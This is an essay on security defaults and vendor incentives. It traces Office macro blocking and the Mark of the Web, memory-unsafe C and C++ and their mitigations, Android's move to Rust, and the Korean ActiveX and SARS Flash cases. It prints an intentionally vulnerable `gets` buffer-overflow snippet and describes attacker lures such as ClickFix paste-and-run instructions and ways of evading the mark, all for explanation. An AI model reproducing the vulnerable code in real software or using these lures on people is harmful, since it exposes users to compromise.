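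Signatures had the same weaknesses as in ActiveX, but they meant users no longer had to decide whether to run unsigned macros. Microsoft (2002) published a January 2002 interview in which one of its managers, Jeanne Sheldon, said that Office XP set every application to High by default. She said this spared people a decision that was "really impossible for the average user to make". Knowing the sender did not help, she explained, because the sender might be forwarding a file without knowing what macros it contained.

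In Office 2007, Microsoft gave users back the decision about whether to run unsigned macros. Earlier versions had disabled these macros without giving users an option to enable them, but Office 2007 notified users and let them do so, according to Microsoft's *Evaluate default security settings and privacy options for the 2007 Office system* (2009).

| Version | What happened by default to an unsigned macro in a stranger's document |
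|---|---|
| Word 6 and Word 95 | It could run without warning |
| Word 97, with macro protection on | The user chose whether to disable it |
| Word 2000, then all of Office XP | Office disabled it without asking |
| Office 2007 | Office disabled it and let the user enable it |
| Office for Windows from July 2022, for files from the internet | Office blocked it and offered no button to enable it |

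Microsoft's *Overview of security in the 2007 Office system* (2009) explains the reversal. Most administrators had settled on a compromise in which Office asked users about macros from unknown sources. Users could not see the document until they answered, so most dismissed the warning to get on with their work, whether the file came from a colleague or a stranger.

Office 2007 opened documents immediately with their macros off and showed a notice about the macros in a strip above the text, called the Message Bar. People who only wanted to read a document no longer had to decide anything. This was an improvement for companies that had been using the Medium setting, but a step back for anyone still on High. Microsoft's own comparison of the old and new versions matches the new default with the old Medium setting.

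### Talking people into the click

Attackers had been telling users to ignore the macro warning since at least 1999. A few days after Melissa, an Excel virus called Papa arrived in emails that said "Urgent info inside. Disregard macro warning", according to Microsoft (1999).

The Message Bar made it easier to trick readers into enabling macros, because the attacker's document was now open below the warning. Attackers added instructions to the document explaining which button to press, often with an arrow pointing to it. Typically they claimed that the reader needed to enable macros to see the content, which was plausible because some legitimate spreadsheets do not work without their macros. Conficker had used a similar deception when it added its own entry to the AutoPlay menu.

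The macro warning described a general risk, while the attacker's text was about an invoice or delivery that the clerk had to deal with. The clerk had probably clicked the same button for legitimate files from suppliers. After one click, Office treated the file as a Trusted Document and did not show the warning for that file again.

By then attackers no longer needed their macros to copy themselves, because they emailed a document containing the macro to each victim. Microsoft had helped to end the old macro viruses by making it harder for macros to spread from the global template into other files. Unlike the makers of exploit kits, these attackers did not need a new flaw each time Adobe or Oracle issued a patch, because the victim's click allowed the macro to run.

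The method appears to have been common, judging by two figures from early 2022. IT Brew reports that the security firm Expel found macro-enabled Word documents or zipped JavaScript files at the start of 82 per cent of the incidents it classed as leading up to ransomware. According to the same article, malicious Office files made up 31 per cent of the malware downloads that another firm, Netskope, blocked. Neither figure counts macros alone, since Expel's includes JavaScript files and Netskope's includes Office files that attack in other ways. Both figures also cover only the firms' own customers.

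### The administrator's switch of 2016

In March 2016, with macro malware rising again, *In the Beginning was the Word* (Martin, 2016) reported that Microsoft had added a policy to Office 2016 that let administrators block macros in files from the internet. Employees could not override the block by clicking.

The policy was off by default, so it protected only employees whose administrator knew about it and had identified the macros that the business needed. A small firm or home user had to find and change the setting by hand. Microsoft still does not offer these policies to customers of Microsoft 365 Apps for business, its edition for smaller companies.

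Ducklin writes that security firms spent years urging Microsoft to let customers install Office without VBA. Microsoft refused because users and reviewers judge a product by what it does when they first install it, and rivals could have presented Office as a suite without macros. Microsoft also held off because some businesses relied on macros.

### How the 2022 block works

Microsoft announced the new default in February 2022. Microsoft product manager Kellie Eickmeyer, whom Thurrott quotes, acknowledged that despite the notification bar "users could still decide to enable the macros by clicking a button". Under the new default, whether macros could run depended mainly on where the file came from and less on the user's judgement.

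To apply it, Office reads the Mark of the Web, a label that Windows attaches to files from the internet, including downloads and email attachments. Windows stores the label beside the file's contents, where the user does not normally see it. The label includes a number for the zone the file came from. Zone 1 is the company's own network, 2 is trusted sites, 3 is the internet and 4 is restricted sites. By default, Windows marks only files from zones 3 and 4.

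Microsoft's *Macros from the internet are blocked by default in Office* sets out what happens when someone opens a marked file that contains macros:

1. Office checks whether the file is in a Trusted Location, a folder that a user or administrator has designated as safe. If it is, the macros run.
2. Office checks for a digital signature. If the computer lists the signer as a trusted publisher, the macros run.
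3. Office checks whether an administrator has set a policy. If so, the policy decides whether the macros run.
4. If there is no policy, Office checks whether the user enabled this file's macros before the new default arrived. If so, they run again.
5. Otherwise Office blocks the macros.

Only the last step changed in 2022. Office had shown a security warning with an "Enable content" button. It now shows a banner headed "Security risk", with a "Learn more" button that leads to an article about the danger.

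Office checks whether a macro comes from a trusted folder or publisher before it applies policy, so trusted macros can run even where the administrator has blocked macros from the internet. Anyone who can save a file to a trusted folder can therefore run code on the computers that open it from there. Trusting a certificate also means trusting every macro signed with it. Microsoft recommends using Trusted Locations sparingly and controlling who can save files to them.

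A user can still remove the mark by right-clicking the file, opening its properties and selecting "Unblock". Ducklin predicted that criminals would coach people through this as well. Unblocking a file takes more steps than clicking the old button and happens outside the document, so fewer people are likely to follow such instructions by accident.

Some files never receive the mark, or lose it. Windows can store it only on disks that use the NTFS format, so a file copied to a FAT32 memory stick loses it. Files that Microsoft's OneDrive service automatically copies to a computer don't have it either. Colleagues can therefore share macros through OneDrive without having them blocked, but so can an attacker who has broken into a colleague's account.

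### Withdrawn and restored in July 2022

Microsoft released the new default to Office's update channels at different times, because some channels give businesses extra time to test changes.

| Date | What happened |
|---|---|
| February 2022 | Microsoft announced the change |
| 12 April 2022 | It began to reach the preview of the Current Channel, which receives updates early |
| 6–7 July 2022 | Microsoft withdrew it from the Current Channel |
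| 20 July 2022 | Microsoft announced that it would resume |
| 27 July 2022 | The Current Channel began to receive it again |
| 11 October 2022 | Monthly Enterprise Channel |
| 10 January 2023 | Semi-Annual Enterprise Channel |
| 14 February 2023 | Publisher, Microsoft's page-layout program |
| 13 August 2024 | Project, its planning program |

The change does not cover Office on Macs, phones, tablets or the web. The Mac omission matters most because Office for Mac can run VBA macros.

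Customers found out about the July withdrawal before Microsoft explained it. The Hacker News (2022) quotes a 6 July comment in which Microsoft employee Angela Robertson confirmed that a rollback had begun and apologised that it had started before the announcement. In a notice to administrators the next day, reproduced in BornCity's *Microsoft does not want to block macros in Office by default* (2022), Microsoft said only that it was acting on feedback. Security researchers objected. In a post reprinted in TechSpot's *Microsoft reverses Office macro blocking, which raises security concerns* (2022), Shane Huntley called the withdrawal a "sad decision" and argued that blocking macros would do far more good than publishing threat research.

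Microsoft never specified the feedback, but its revised instructions suggest what had gone wrong. They explained what to do with files on a network share or on SharePoint, Microsoft's service for storing documents online. Many companies treated these locations as internal, but Windows could classify them as the internet. Even a server in the same building could fall outside the trusted zone if employees connected to it by its numerical address. Because the mark recorded a file's route rather than its owner, a company's own files could be marked as coming from the internet.

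Office Watch's *Inside the Office VBA/Mark of the Web changes* (2022) compared Microsoft's instructions from before and after the suspension. Microsoft had added about a thousand words, mostly a table of ways to unblock files. Office Watch argued that Microsoft could have improved the instructions while leaving the block in place. This seems right, because the default that returned on 27 July worked essentially the same way. The suspension gave administrators three more weeks to sort out their shared folders, but those who wanted the block could already set it by policy, and home users were without it until the default returned.

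### The fall in macro attacks

The security company Proofpoint, which filters email for businesses, reported in *How Threat Actors Are Adapting to a Post-Macro World* (2022) that the use of macro-enabled attachments fell by about 66 per cent between October 2021 and June 2022. Its researchers counted campaigns, meaning groups of malicious emails they had analysed by hand. Computer Weekly's *Cyber criminals pivot away from macros as Microsoft changes bite* (2022) gives approximate counts.

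| Type of campaign | October 2021 | June 2022 |
|---|---|---|
| VBA macros | Just under 70 | Just over 21 |
| Container files and shortcuts | About 70 | Close to 200 |
| Shortcut files alone | Under 10 | Just over 70 |

Container files, such as zip archives and disc images, hold other files. The number of campaigns using Windows shortcuts rose from about four to 71, an increase of 1,675 per cent.

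This period ended before the block reached most people. By the end of June, only the Current Channel preview had officially started to receive the VBA change, and business channels were still months from getting it. Excel's XL4 macros were a partial exception. Microsoft had announced restrictions on them in October 2021, and Neowin's *Microsoft strangely backtracks on decision to block Office macros by default* dates the start of those restrictions to January 2022. The general change of default therefore cannot have directly caused the fall, which followed Microsoft's announcements and some partial blocks.

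Sherrod DeGrippo, who led threat research at Proofpoint, said that attackers began looking for ways around the block as soon as Microsoft announced it. Her explanation fits the dates. It also fits the lack of any visible recovery in macro attacks when Microsoft withdrew the block in July, although the withdrawal lasted only about three weeks.

A few large groups can also move the figures a lot. The use of XL4 macros jumped in March 2022, for example, probably because the group behind the Emotet malware sent more campaigns that month. The counts don't measure how many people received each campaign or were infected. Microsoft, which could see what happened on customers' computers, declined to comment on the fall, according to The Record's *Hacker use of Microsoft macros plummeted after default block* (2022).

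### Where the attackers went

Attackers used container files to avoid the mark. Windows marked a downloaded disc image but not the files inside it. If the image contained an Excel file with a macro, Office treated the file as local and showed the old warning with its button. Many attackers replaced the macro with a shortcut that started the malware when the victim double-clicked it. The Record reports that state-backed groups from Russia and North Korea also used shortcuts. Proofpoint had also expected a rise in malicious Excel add-ins, but found only a slight one.

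In November 2022 Microsoft issued a Windows security update, with a CVE number, that applied the Mark of the Web to files inside disc images. Microsoft had not classed macros as a vulnerability, but once it relied on the mark to block them, it treated a way to bypass the mark as one.

Attackers next turned to OneNote, Microsoft's note-taking program, which does not run VBA macros and was not part of the change. In the winter of 2022 to 2023 criminals attached scripts to OneNote pages, covered them with a picture of a button and asked the reader to double-click it. OneNote displayed a warning, which people clicked through as they had in Word. In spring 2023 Microsoft began blocking the most dangerous types of attachment in OneNote.

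Other attackers looked for bugs in how programs handled the mark. These were ordinary bugs that could be fixed, unlike the weakness in macros themselves. A deliberately malformed digital signature made Windows skip its warning about a marked file, which Microsoft patched in December 2022. The archive program 7-Zip failed to pass the mark to files in nested archives until its developer fixed the problem in late 2024.

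From 2024 attackers used a method called ClickFix that avoided marked files altogether, and they were still using it in 2026. A web page shows a false error message or a fake test to prove that the visitor is human. It copies a command to the visitor's clipboard and shows instructions to press Windows+R, Ctrl+V and Enter. These keystrokes open the Windows Run box, paste the command and run it. Windows receives the command as if the user had typed it, and the command downloads the malware.

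ClickFix is harder to restrict than OneNote attachments. Administrators can disable the command box for employees who do not need it, and security software can block commands that look suspicious. But technicians and programmers paste commands from web pages every day, so Microsoft could not block pasting altogether without disrupting their work.

### Did total harm fall?

Macros became a much less common way to break into computers, and the block makes a return to their former level unlikely. Whether fewer people suffered attacks is much less clear. Proofpoint counted over 100 more campaigns using containers and shortcuts, and about 50 fewer using VBA macros. The two groups overlap, because some containers held documents with macros, and the counts leave out the separate decline in XL4 macros. Even so, they don't suggest that attackers sent fewer malicious emails.

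Proofpoint's campaign counts record what attackers tried, so they cannot show whether fewer attempts succeeded after July 2022. Infection rates for all malware that arrived by email or through web pages, before and after that month, would come much closer to answering the question. Microsoft published similar rates for AutoRun, based on hundreds of millions of computers.

Harm per attempt probably fell somewhat. People opened Word documents all day, but a disc image or a request to paste a command is unfamiliar enough to make some of them stop. Microsoft could also restrict some of the replacements with little disruption to honest users, since hardly anyone's work depended on opening a script from a OneNote page. However, ClickFix has needed neither an unpatched flaw nor an attachment, and ransomware gangs could still buy stolen passwords instead of emailing victims. Total harm therefore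 probably fell by much less than the use of macros did, and it may not have fallen at all.

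## Memory-unsafe languages, the class that was never withdrawn

Microsoft blocked macros in files from the internet, a feature that most recipients of those files never needed. But withdrawing the memory-unsafe languages C and C++ would have meant withdrawing most of Windows, the main browsers and the Flash player, which were written in them. Engineers have known about the danger since at least 1972, and both languages are still among the most widely used.

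### Eight bytes for a name

Suppose a server asks visitors for their names, and its programmer has written these two lines of C:

`char name[8];`

`gets(name);`

The first line sets aside eight bytes of memory. The second calls `gets`, which copies a line of text from the visitor into that space. `gets` receives the address where the space begins but not its length, so it keeps copying until the visitor's line ends.

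The program keeps `name` in an area of memory called the stack. The stack also holds the return address, which tells the processor where to continue when the current function finishes. A simplified layout looks like this:

| Bytes | Normal contents | After a visitor sends a hostile line |
|---|---|---|
| 1–8 | The visitor's name | Filler |
| 9–16 | Notes for the function that made the call | Filler |
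| 17–24 | The return address | An address the attacker chose |
| 25 onwards | Other data | The attacker's own instructions |

When the function finishes, the processor jumps to the attacker's address and runs the instructions there with the program's privileges. Engineers call this a buffer overflow. Other memory errors include reading past the end of a buffer, which can reveal secrets, and use-after-free, which was common in Flash.

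van der Veen, dutt-Sharma and colleagues, in *Memory Errors*, a history of these attacks, describe storing a user's data beside the program's control information as in-band signalling, the mistake behind the blue box. But a program can check whether a name is longer than eight bytes, whereas an exchange could not tell a caller's tone from its own. Each overflow therefore has an easy patch. A large program has thousands of places where a programmer must remember the check, and an attacker needs only one where somebody forgot.

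### Why nobody could patch the language

C does not check whether a program stays within an array. *Memory Safety*, a set of Columbia University lecture slides, includes an example that treats an array of characters as a function and runs it. The lecturer compiled it with gcc, a widely used C compiler, and got no warning.

*Buffer Overflows* (2015), a summary of a paper from 2000, explains that checking every read and write would stop buffer overflows completely. But the tools that added such checks to C by 2000 either missed many cases or slowed programs severely. The main obstacle is that a C program usually refers to a buffer only by its starting address. A compiler would have to attach a length to every such address, which would change how programs lay out their data and pass it to one another. New code would then not work with libraries that were already compiled.

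C also has no single owner who could send out an update, as Microsoft did for AutoRun. Many organisations make compilers, and a new compiler doesn't change an existing program until somebody rebuilds it.

Safer designs existed. The developers of Multics, an operating system begun in the 1960s, wrote most of it in the language PL/I, which together with the hardware made buffer overflows rare. C spread with a different operating system, Unix.

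### From a 1972 study to the 1988 worm

Shostack + Friends' *Buffer Overflows and History* (2008) quotes James Anderson's 1972 planning study, which described a system routine that did not check addresses properly. Anderson wrote that a user could exploit this to "inject code into the monitor", the program that controlled the machine, and take over the machine.

The public warning came on 2 November 1988, when Robert T. Morris, a graduate student, released a worm that spread across the internet. One of its methods was to send an overlong line to `fingerd`, a service that gave out information about a computer's users. The service read the line with `gets`, and the line overflowed the buffer. The worm also guessed passwords and exploited a debugging option in a mail program. It affected an estimated 3,000 to 6,000 machines, or 5 to 10 per cent of the internet.

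In *The Internet Worm Program*, published within a month of the worm, Spafford (1988) recommended replacing `gets` and similar routines with versions that take a length. This would have taken little work in Berkeley's version of Unix, since an audit found only two of its servers using `gets`. But experienced programmers kept using these routines despite knowing the risk, and the committee standardising C was about to include them in the standard. The C standard did not drop `gets` until 2011. Fifteen years after the worm, in *A Failure to Learn from the Past*, Spafford traced more than a quarter of newly reported flaws to buffer overflows and called it "appalling" that companies still shipped them.

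Defences became common only after others had published the method in detail. In 1996 Elias Levy, writing as Aleph One, explained it step by step in *Phrack* magazine.

### Six mitigations and how attackers got past them

**Stack canaries**, which researchers proposed in 1998, are hard-to-guess values that the compiler puts just before return addresses. The program checks the canary when the function finishes. An overflow that reaches the return address has to overwrite the canary first, so the check fails and the program stops. Canaries don't help if the attacker can overwrite the return address without touching the canary, or can make the program reveal the canary. David Litchfield found another way around the check on Windows, by overwriting the address of the routine that Windows ran after the check failed.

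**Non-executable memory** stops the processor from running instructions stored in areas meant for data, so the code in the hostile line above would not run. Alexander Peslyak, known as Solar Designer, released a version for Linux in 1997, and Microsoft added the protection to Windows XP in 2004. Within months of his release, Peslyak published a way to bypass it. The attacker leaves out the new code and sets the return address to a useful function that the program already contains. Others later learned to chain short fragments of existing code to do almost anything.

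With address randomisation, the operating system loads the parts of a program at different addresses each time, because attackers need to know where the program's code is to reuse it. The first version appeared in 2001. Most systems moved whole regions of memory without rearranging their contents, so an attacker who learned one address could work out the others nearby. Attackers therefore began looking for a second bug that leaks an address.

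**Sandboxed processes.** A browser can handle a web page or picture in a separate process with few permissions. The operating system enforces the boundary, which it did not do for Java's sandbox. CISA's *The Case for Memory Safe Roadmaps* (2023), joint guidance from agencies in five countries, says that attackers often find ways to escape. Each extra sandbox also makes the program more complex, and a phone can run only a limited number.

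**Fuzzing.** Testers feed a program malformed input to find crashes, as Dormann and Plakosh did with ActiveX controls. This removes bugs instead of making them harder to exploit. Google (2024) reported that its free fuzzing service for open-source software had helped find and fix more than 8,800 vulnerabilities in 850 projects. But a fuzzer finds only the bugs its inputs trigger, and researchers still discover flaws in heavily fuzzed code.

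Memory tagging attaches a small number to each block of memory and the same number to the addresses that may refer to it, and the processor stops the program if the two differ. Arm, which designs most phone processors, published its version in 2019. *Optimized Memory Tagging on AmpereOne Processors* (2025) explains that tagging always stops an overflow from one block into the next if the software gives neighbouring blocks different tags. A use-after-free may go undetected because the four-bit tag has only sixteen possible values. If software picked tags at random, about one reused block in sixteen would match by chance.

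Attackers can also try to learn the tags. *TikTag* (2024) exploited the way processors run some instructions before establishing whether they are needed. This leaked tags and bypassed the protection in Chrome and the Linux kernel, the core of that operating system. According to Apple's blog post *Memory Integrity Enforcement* (2025), the company judged Arm's original version too weak to use as a live defence and worked on a stronger one, which it has built into every iPhone 17 and iPhone Air, with measures to keep the tags secret. The security company Calif has since announced what it calls the first public exploit of kernel memory corruption on Apple hardware with this protection.

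### A more expensive attack

In 1996, an attacker needed one buffer overflow and published instructions for exploiting it. An attacker targeting a modern browser would probably need a memory error to get started, a leak that reveals where the program's code is in memory, and another flaw to escape the sandbox. Patching any one of these can break the whole attack. Criminals who want to infect thousands of ordinary computers may find it cheaper to buy passwords or send a fake error message.

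Well-funded attackers still exploit memory errors. CISA's 2023 guidance cites a Google Project Zero analysis in which 67 per cent of the zero-day flaws recorded in 2021 were memory errors. That figure covers only detected attacks, and some kinds of flaw may be easier to detect than others.

Researchers have disagreed about how much the defences achieved. Van der Veen and colleagues recall that in 2011 one expert reviewing papers for a leading security conference considered the problem mostly solved, while a reviewer for another doubted the usefulness of research that had failed to solve it. Their data showed fewer reported memory errors after 2007 but no matching decline in exploits. Possibly the easy bugs disappeared while attackers kept using the rest. Van der Veen and colleagues tentatively concluded that memory errors were unlikely to become much less important soon.

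Part of the difficulty is that every layer of defence slows programs or needs continuing work. Arm estimates that memory tagging slows programs by only 1 to 2 per cent, but developers must also sort through fuzzing results, maintain sandboxes and keep issuing patches.

### Seventy per cent

About 70 per cent of the vulnerabilities to which Microsoft assigned CVE numbers between 2006 and 2018 were memory errors, as were about 70 per cent of those in Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome. In one analysis of Mozilla's vulnerabilities, 32 of the 34 most serious bugs were memory errors. These older figures come from products written largely in C and C++, so they do not describe software in general.

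Memory-safety bugs made up an even higher share of the vulnerabilities in Google's Android phone operating system in 2019, at 76 per cent. Around that time its developers began writing new parts in memory-safe languages. Much of Android already used two such languages, Java and Kotlin, but the lowest layers need close control of the hardware, so Google introduced Rust for them. The Rust compiler tracks which part of a program may use each piece of memory and rejects code that breaks the rules. The finished program also checks array positions as it runs, so an overlong name would stop the program instead of overwriting the return address.

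Google (2024) reported that the share had fallen to 24 per cent. The number of memory errors fell from 223 in 2019 to a projected 36 in 2024, despite a slight rise in 2023. Dark Reading's *Memory-Safe Code Adoption Has Made Android Safer* (2024) describes the 2024 figure as about half the previous year's count. In November 2025, Vander Stoep's *Rust in Android* reported a share below 20 per cent for the first time.

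Memory errors' share of Android vulnerabilities fell partly because other flaws increased. The percentages imply that Android had about 290 vulnerabilities of all kinds in 2019 and 150 in 2024. Those that were not memory errors rose from about 70 to about 115, perhaps because there was more code. Rust does not prevent flaws such as a missing permission check. Even so, the total fell by nearly half, and Google describes memory errors as usually more severe and easier to exploit remotely than other flaws.

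Rust was not the only cause of the decline in memory errors, because Google was also hardening its C and C++ code during these years. But the decline matches the change of language, since the share of memory errors fell with the share of new code written in memory-unsafe languages.

### Why replacing only new code works

Most of Android's code was still memory-unsafe in 2024. Memory errors had declined even though Google left the old code largely unchanged, apart from fixing bugs.

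The explanation is that most vulnerabilities are in new or recently changed code. As code ages, people find and fix its bugs, and the number left falls roughly exponentially. If vulnerabilities survive for λ years on average, the density after t years is

D(t) = D(0) × e^(−t/λ)

Google's simulation used an average vulnerability lifetime of 2.5 years. At that rate, code unchanged for five years has e^(−2), or about 0.14, of its original vulnerability density, which is 7.4 times lower than that of new code. A study of open-source software found longer lifetimes, which give a factor of 3.4.

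The simulated program doubled in size every six years, and its developers took ten years to move new work to safe languages. Unsafe code kept growing during the change, but memory errors dropped sharply because developers added fewer bugs each year and kept removing old ones.

This decay depends on somebody looking for the bugs. Attackers kept exploiting Flash's obsolete ActionScript engine, for example. Code in a widely studied product such as Android gets safer as it ages, but code in a forgotten library or a cheap router may not.

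The method also requires new Rust code to work with old C++, so Google invested in tools that connect the two and gave $1 million to the Rust Foundation. Chromium's developers replaced the components that read PNG images, JSON data and web fonts with Rust versions, because all three handle data from untrusted sources.

### One near miss in five million lines

Rust lets programmers mark a block of code as `unsafe`, which permits operations that the compiler cannot verify, such as controlling hardware directly. About 4 per cent of Android's Rust code is in such blocks.

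In 2025 Google found a buffer overflow in CrabbyAVIF, a Rust component for reading images, before the bug reached a public release. Android's memory allocator places guard pages, which no program may touch, around large blocks of memory it gives to programs. The overflow would have hit a guard page and crashed the program without giving an attacker control. Google still assigned the bug a CVE number so that partners would treat the patch as urgent.

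Counting this case, Vander Stoep put the rate for Rust at 0.2 potential vulnerabilities per million lines (one in about 5 million), compared with a historical rate of about 1,000 per million for Android's C and C++. He claims a reduction of more than a thousandfold. An estimate based on one bug is fragile, and researchers have had much less time to examine the Rust code. But even if they eventually found fifty such bugs, the rate would be ten per million lines, about a hundredth of the rate for C and C++.

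Rust did not slow developers down either. Android's developers rolled back medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often as C++ changes, and Rust changes spent about 25 per cent less time in review. Google compared changes of similar size made by overlapping groups of engineers, but it could not fully rule out that teams chose Rust for work that was easier to get right.

### Pressure from governments, and the objections

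*Software Memory Safety* (2023), which the US National Security Agency (NSA) first issued in 2022, recommended memory-safe languages "when possible" and acknowledged that they do not give absolute protection. In December 2023 American agencies joined those of Australia, Canada, Britain and New Zealand in asking every software maker to publish a memory safety roadmap. The roadmap should set dates for each phase, including one after which the company would write new code only in a memory-safe language. The agencies wanted a chief executive or other senior manager to sign it because they considered the problem one of business strategy. In June 2025 the NSA and CISA published a guide to the obstacles companies face in adopting these languages, which CISA announced in *New Guidance Released for Reducing Memory-Related Vulnerabilities* (2025). Software makers are not required to follow any of this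 advice.

The most common objection is the cost of rewriting. The agencies conceded in 2025 that memory-unsafe languages "remain practical necessities" in places, according to ITPro's *Want to build more secure software*. Companies depend on C and C++ libraries that nobody will replace soon, and calling them from safe code weakens the guarantee of memory safety. Many small industrial devices have few safe languages to choose from. Languages such as Java periodically clean up unused memory, which can cause pauses that a real-time system cannot tolerate.

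A rewrite can also introduce new bugs. Programmers may have spent twenty years correcting an old component, and its replacement could mishandle an unusual file that the original handles correctly. The agencies suggest running both versions side by side and comparing the results before retiring the old one. Google's figures on ageing code strengthen the objection about new bugs, because rewriting five-year-old code removes far fewer vulnerabilities per line than writing new code safely prevents. They also weaken the objection about cost, because they show that a company can get most of the benefit without a full rewrite.

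Some C and C++ developers would rather make their languages safer. Apple changed the C compiler for iBoot, the software that starts its devices, and Microsoft developed Checked C, which adds bounds checks. Outside analysis suggests that Apple's approach may noticeably slow programs and increase their memory use. These projects would let companies keep their code and their programmers' skills, but they face the same conflict as earlier attempts to add checks to C, because rules strict enough to prevent the errors would reject much existing code.

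### Was there a choice?

For a long time, developers of operating systems and browsers could hardly avoid tolerating memory errors. CISA notes that until a few years ago no language combined the speed of C and C++ with built-in memory safety. A Mozilla engineer began work on Rust in 2006, and its first stable version came out in 2015. A browser maker in 2005 could only reduce the harm, which was practical because most mitigations required a rebuild or a system update but few changes to the programs. AI agents also raise the question of whether a safer substitute exists.

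This defence never covered everything. Replacing `gets` took little work in 1988, and many business programs did not need C's speed, so their makers could have used Java from 1995. It also does not cover a company that starts writing a new image reader in C++ today, unless memory-safe languages do not yet support the device it is writing for.

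## How business compatibility kept insecure features alive

Cost was one reason companies kept C and C++, and it also prolonged the use of features that did have safer substitutes. When a vendor removes a feature, the programs and websites built on it stop working at once, and their owners know to complain to the vendor. If the vendor keeps the feature, the harm comes later, to scattered victims who seldom learn how the attacker got in.

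### Who guards the system and who pays

In 2001 the Cambridge security engineer Ross Anderson argued in *Why Information Security is Hard* that incentives cause at least as much insecurity as technical failings. In *The Threat* he summarized the problem: "when Alice guards a system and Bob pays the cost of failure, things break." The first example in the 2001 paper was fraud at cash machines. If an American customer disputed a withdrawal, the bank had to prove that the customer was mistaken or lying. In Britain, Norway and the Netherlands the customer had to prove the bank wrong, which was almost impossible, so banks there grew careless and epidemics of fraud followed. American banks spent less on security and suffered much less fraud.

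A software vendor guards a feature in this sense because it chooses the feature's default setting. Anderson also explained why vendors listen so closely to the companies that build on their products. Customers choose a platform partly for the programs available on it, so the vendor tries even harder to attract developers than users. Strict security makes developers' work harder, which makes the platform less valuable to them. Once customers have invested in those programs, switching to a rival is expensive, so the vendor can keep charging them.

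Anderson's argument about how insecure products reach the market also applies to removing insecure features. If a removal breaks a customer's system, the customer must pay to rebuild it, and can rebuild it on a rival's product for much the same money.

### A worked example

As a hypothetical example, suppose 200 companies depend on an insecure feature of an office program, and replacing what they built on it would cost each of them $50,000, or $10 million in total. Attackers use the feature to steal $1,000 each from 20,000 people a year, or $20 million. Removing the feature would prevent enough theft to cover the replacement cost within six months. The feature could still survive even if nobody involved were careless or greedy.

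| Who decides | Cost of acting | Cost of doing nothing | Sensible choice |
|---|---|---|---|
| The vendor | $2 million a year in lost sales, if 20 of the 200 companies leave and each had paid $100,000 a year | Close to nothing, since few victims blame the feature | Keep the feature |
| A dependent company | $50,000 now | $2,000 a year in expected losses from attacks | Wait, since replacement would take 25 years to pay off |
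| A victim | Several thousand dollars to trace the attack and sue | $1,000, already lost | Accept the loss |

The longer a vendor waits, the harder the feature is to remove. If 20 more companies build on it each year, the number that depend on it will grow from 200 to 300 in five years. Replacing it would then cost $15 million, and the vendor could lose $3 million a year by removing it.

The vendor would drop the feature if it had to pay more than a tenth of the victims' losses, because keeping it would then cost more than the sales lost by removing it. It would also drop the feature if every rival did so by the same date, as the browser makers agreed to do with Flash.

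Removing an insecure feature isn't always worthwhile. In the example, if attackers stole only $200,000 a year, removal would take 50 years to pay for itself. Vendors usually knew which customers were angry better than they knew how much harm a feature caused. AutoRun was unusual because Microsoft had counted the infections.

### South Korea and ActiveX

In South Korea, the government created the dependence on ActiveX. During the 1990s the United States restricted the encryption in exported browsers to keys of 40 and later 56 bits, which were too short to protect bank transfers. The Korean government funded a stronger cipher of its own, SEED, and in 1999 launched internet banking based on digital certificates from approved authorities. Browsers did not support SEED, so banks had to supply it as a plugin. They built it as an ActiveX control because most customers used Internet Explorer. *On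 the Security of Internet Banking in South Korea* (Kim, Huh and Anderson, 2011) reports that customers also had to install an antivirus program, a firewall and software that encrypted their keystrokes.

The United States relaxed its export rules around 2000, but the Korean system stayed. A decade later, over 90 per cent of Korean browsing still went through Internet Explorer, and people could not use their smartphones for banking. Kim and colleagues thought the extra software improved security modestly at best. In one case, two thieves used keyloggers, which record typing, to steal 450 million won (about $386,000) from 86 accounts. In a survey of about 260 users, 84 per cent had seen the plugins fail to install and 69 per cent wanted them made optional. The respondents were younger and better educated than most bank customers, so the survey may overstate discontent among customers in general.

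Pressure to change the law came partly from lost sales. In 2014, Chinese fans of a Korean television drama wanted to buy the coat its star had worn, but could not pay because Korean shops required a Korean certificate. According to the broadcaster SBS in *올해는 정말 설치형 보안 프로그램 지옥에서 벗어날 수 있을까?*, the president raised the matter and regulators dropped the certificate rule for online card payments. That year legislators also revised a law that, according to *A Case Study of the 2016 Korean Cyber Command Compromise* (2017), had barred banks and shops from using alternative security software. The government then aimed to remove ActiveX from 90 of the 100 most popular websites by 2017, The Paypers reported in *South Korea dismisses ActiveX payment requirement* (2015).

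Banks replaced the ActiveX controls with ordinary Windows programs that did the same jobs. When a customer visits the bank's site, a script on the page tries to contact the program. If it gets no response, the site sends the customer to an installation page. Once installed, the program starts with the computer and runs outside the browser's sandbox, waiting for requests from web pages. The change let customers use any browser but left their computers exposed.

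*Too Much of a Good Thing*, a 2025 study of these programs by Yun, Jeong and colleagues, found 19 vulnerabilities, which the makers have since patched. Two programs meant to stop keyloggers could let a hostile web page record what the user typed. The patches may not reach everyone, since the 48 personal computers the researchers examined had an average of nine such programs each, many of them versions from 2022 or earlier. North Korean attackers exploited flaws in this kind of software in 2023 and, by a count the study cites, broke into 61 institutions.

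The law no longer required the software by then, but 13 of the 17 leading banks told customers it was mandatory (two of those let people log in without it). Yun and colleagues think the cost of switching is the likely reason.

In 2026 regulators asked financial firms to submit replacement plans by April and finish the change within the year, according to ZDNet Korea's *에버스핀, AI-MTD 기반 ‘비설치형 보안’으로 금융시장 공략 박차*. At the end of March, SBS found that 6 of 18 banks offered internet banking without installed software. Firms complained about the short deadline and worried about who would be liable for fraud. In 2011, Kim and colleagues had proposed that regulators require banks to reimburse defrauded customers and let the banks choose their security measures. Whoever chose the software would then pay if it failed, as under the American rule on cash machines.

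### Taxes that needed a plugin

The South African Revenue Service (SARS) had more than three years' notice that Flash would end. It converted its busiest tax forms to HTML5 first and planned to convert the rest during 2021, believing that Flash would keep working after Adobe's support ended. On 12 January 2021, a block that Adobe had built into Flash stopped the remaining forms from working. Six days later, SARS (2021) apologised "unreservedly" and admitted that it had misunderstood what the end of support meant.

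On 24 January SARS released its own web browser, which could still run Flash (*Update on Adobe Flash player issues*, 2021). A spokesperson quoted in Stuff (2021) said that the browser was an interim measure for six forms and that SARS had already converted 44. Taxpayers got a filing extension until 15 February. SARS had converted the last forms by December. It withdrew the browser from 13 December and sent stakeholders a letter encouraging people to uninstall it.

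A browser meant for one trusted website is much less risky than leaving Flash on in everyday browsing, provided people use it only for that website. SARS also did the work in a sensible order. But despite the long notice, it had not converted the last six forms, and it discovered its mistake only when Flash stopped working.

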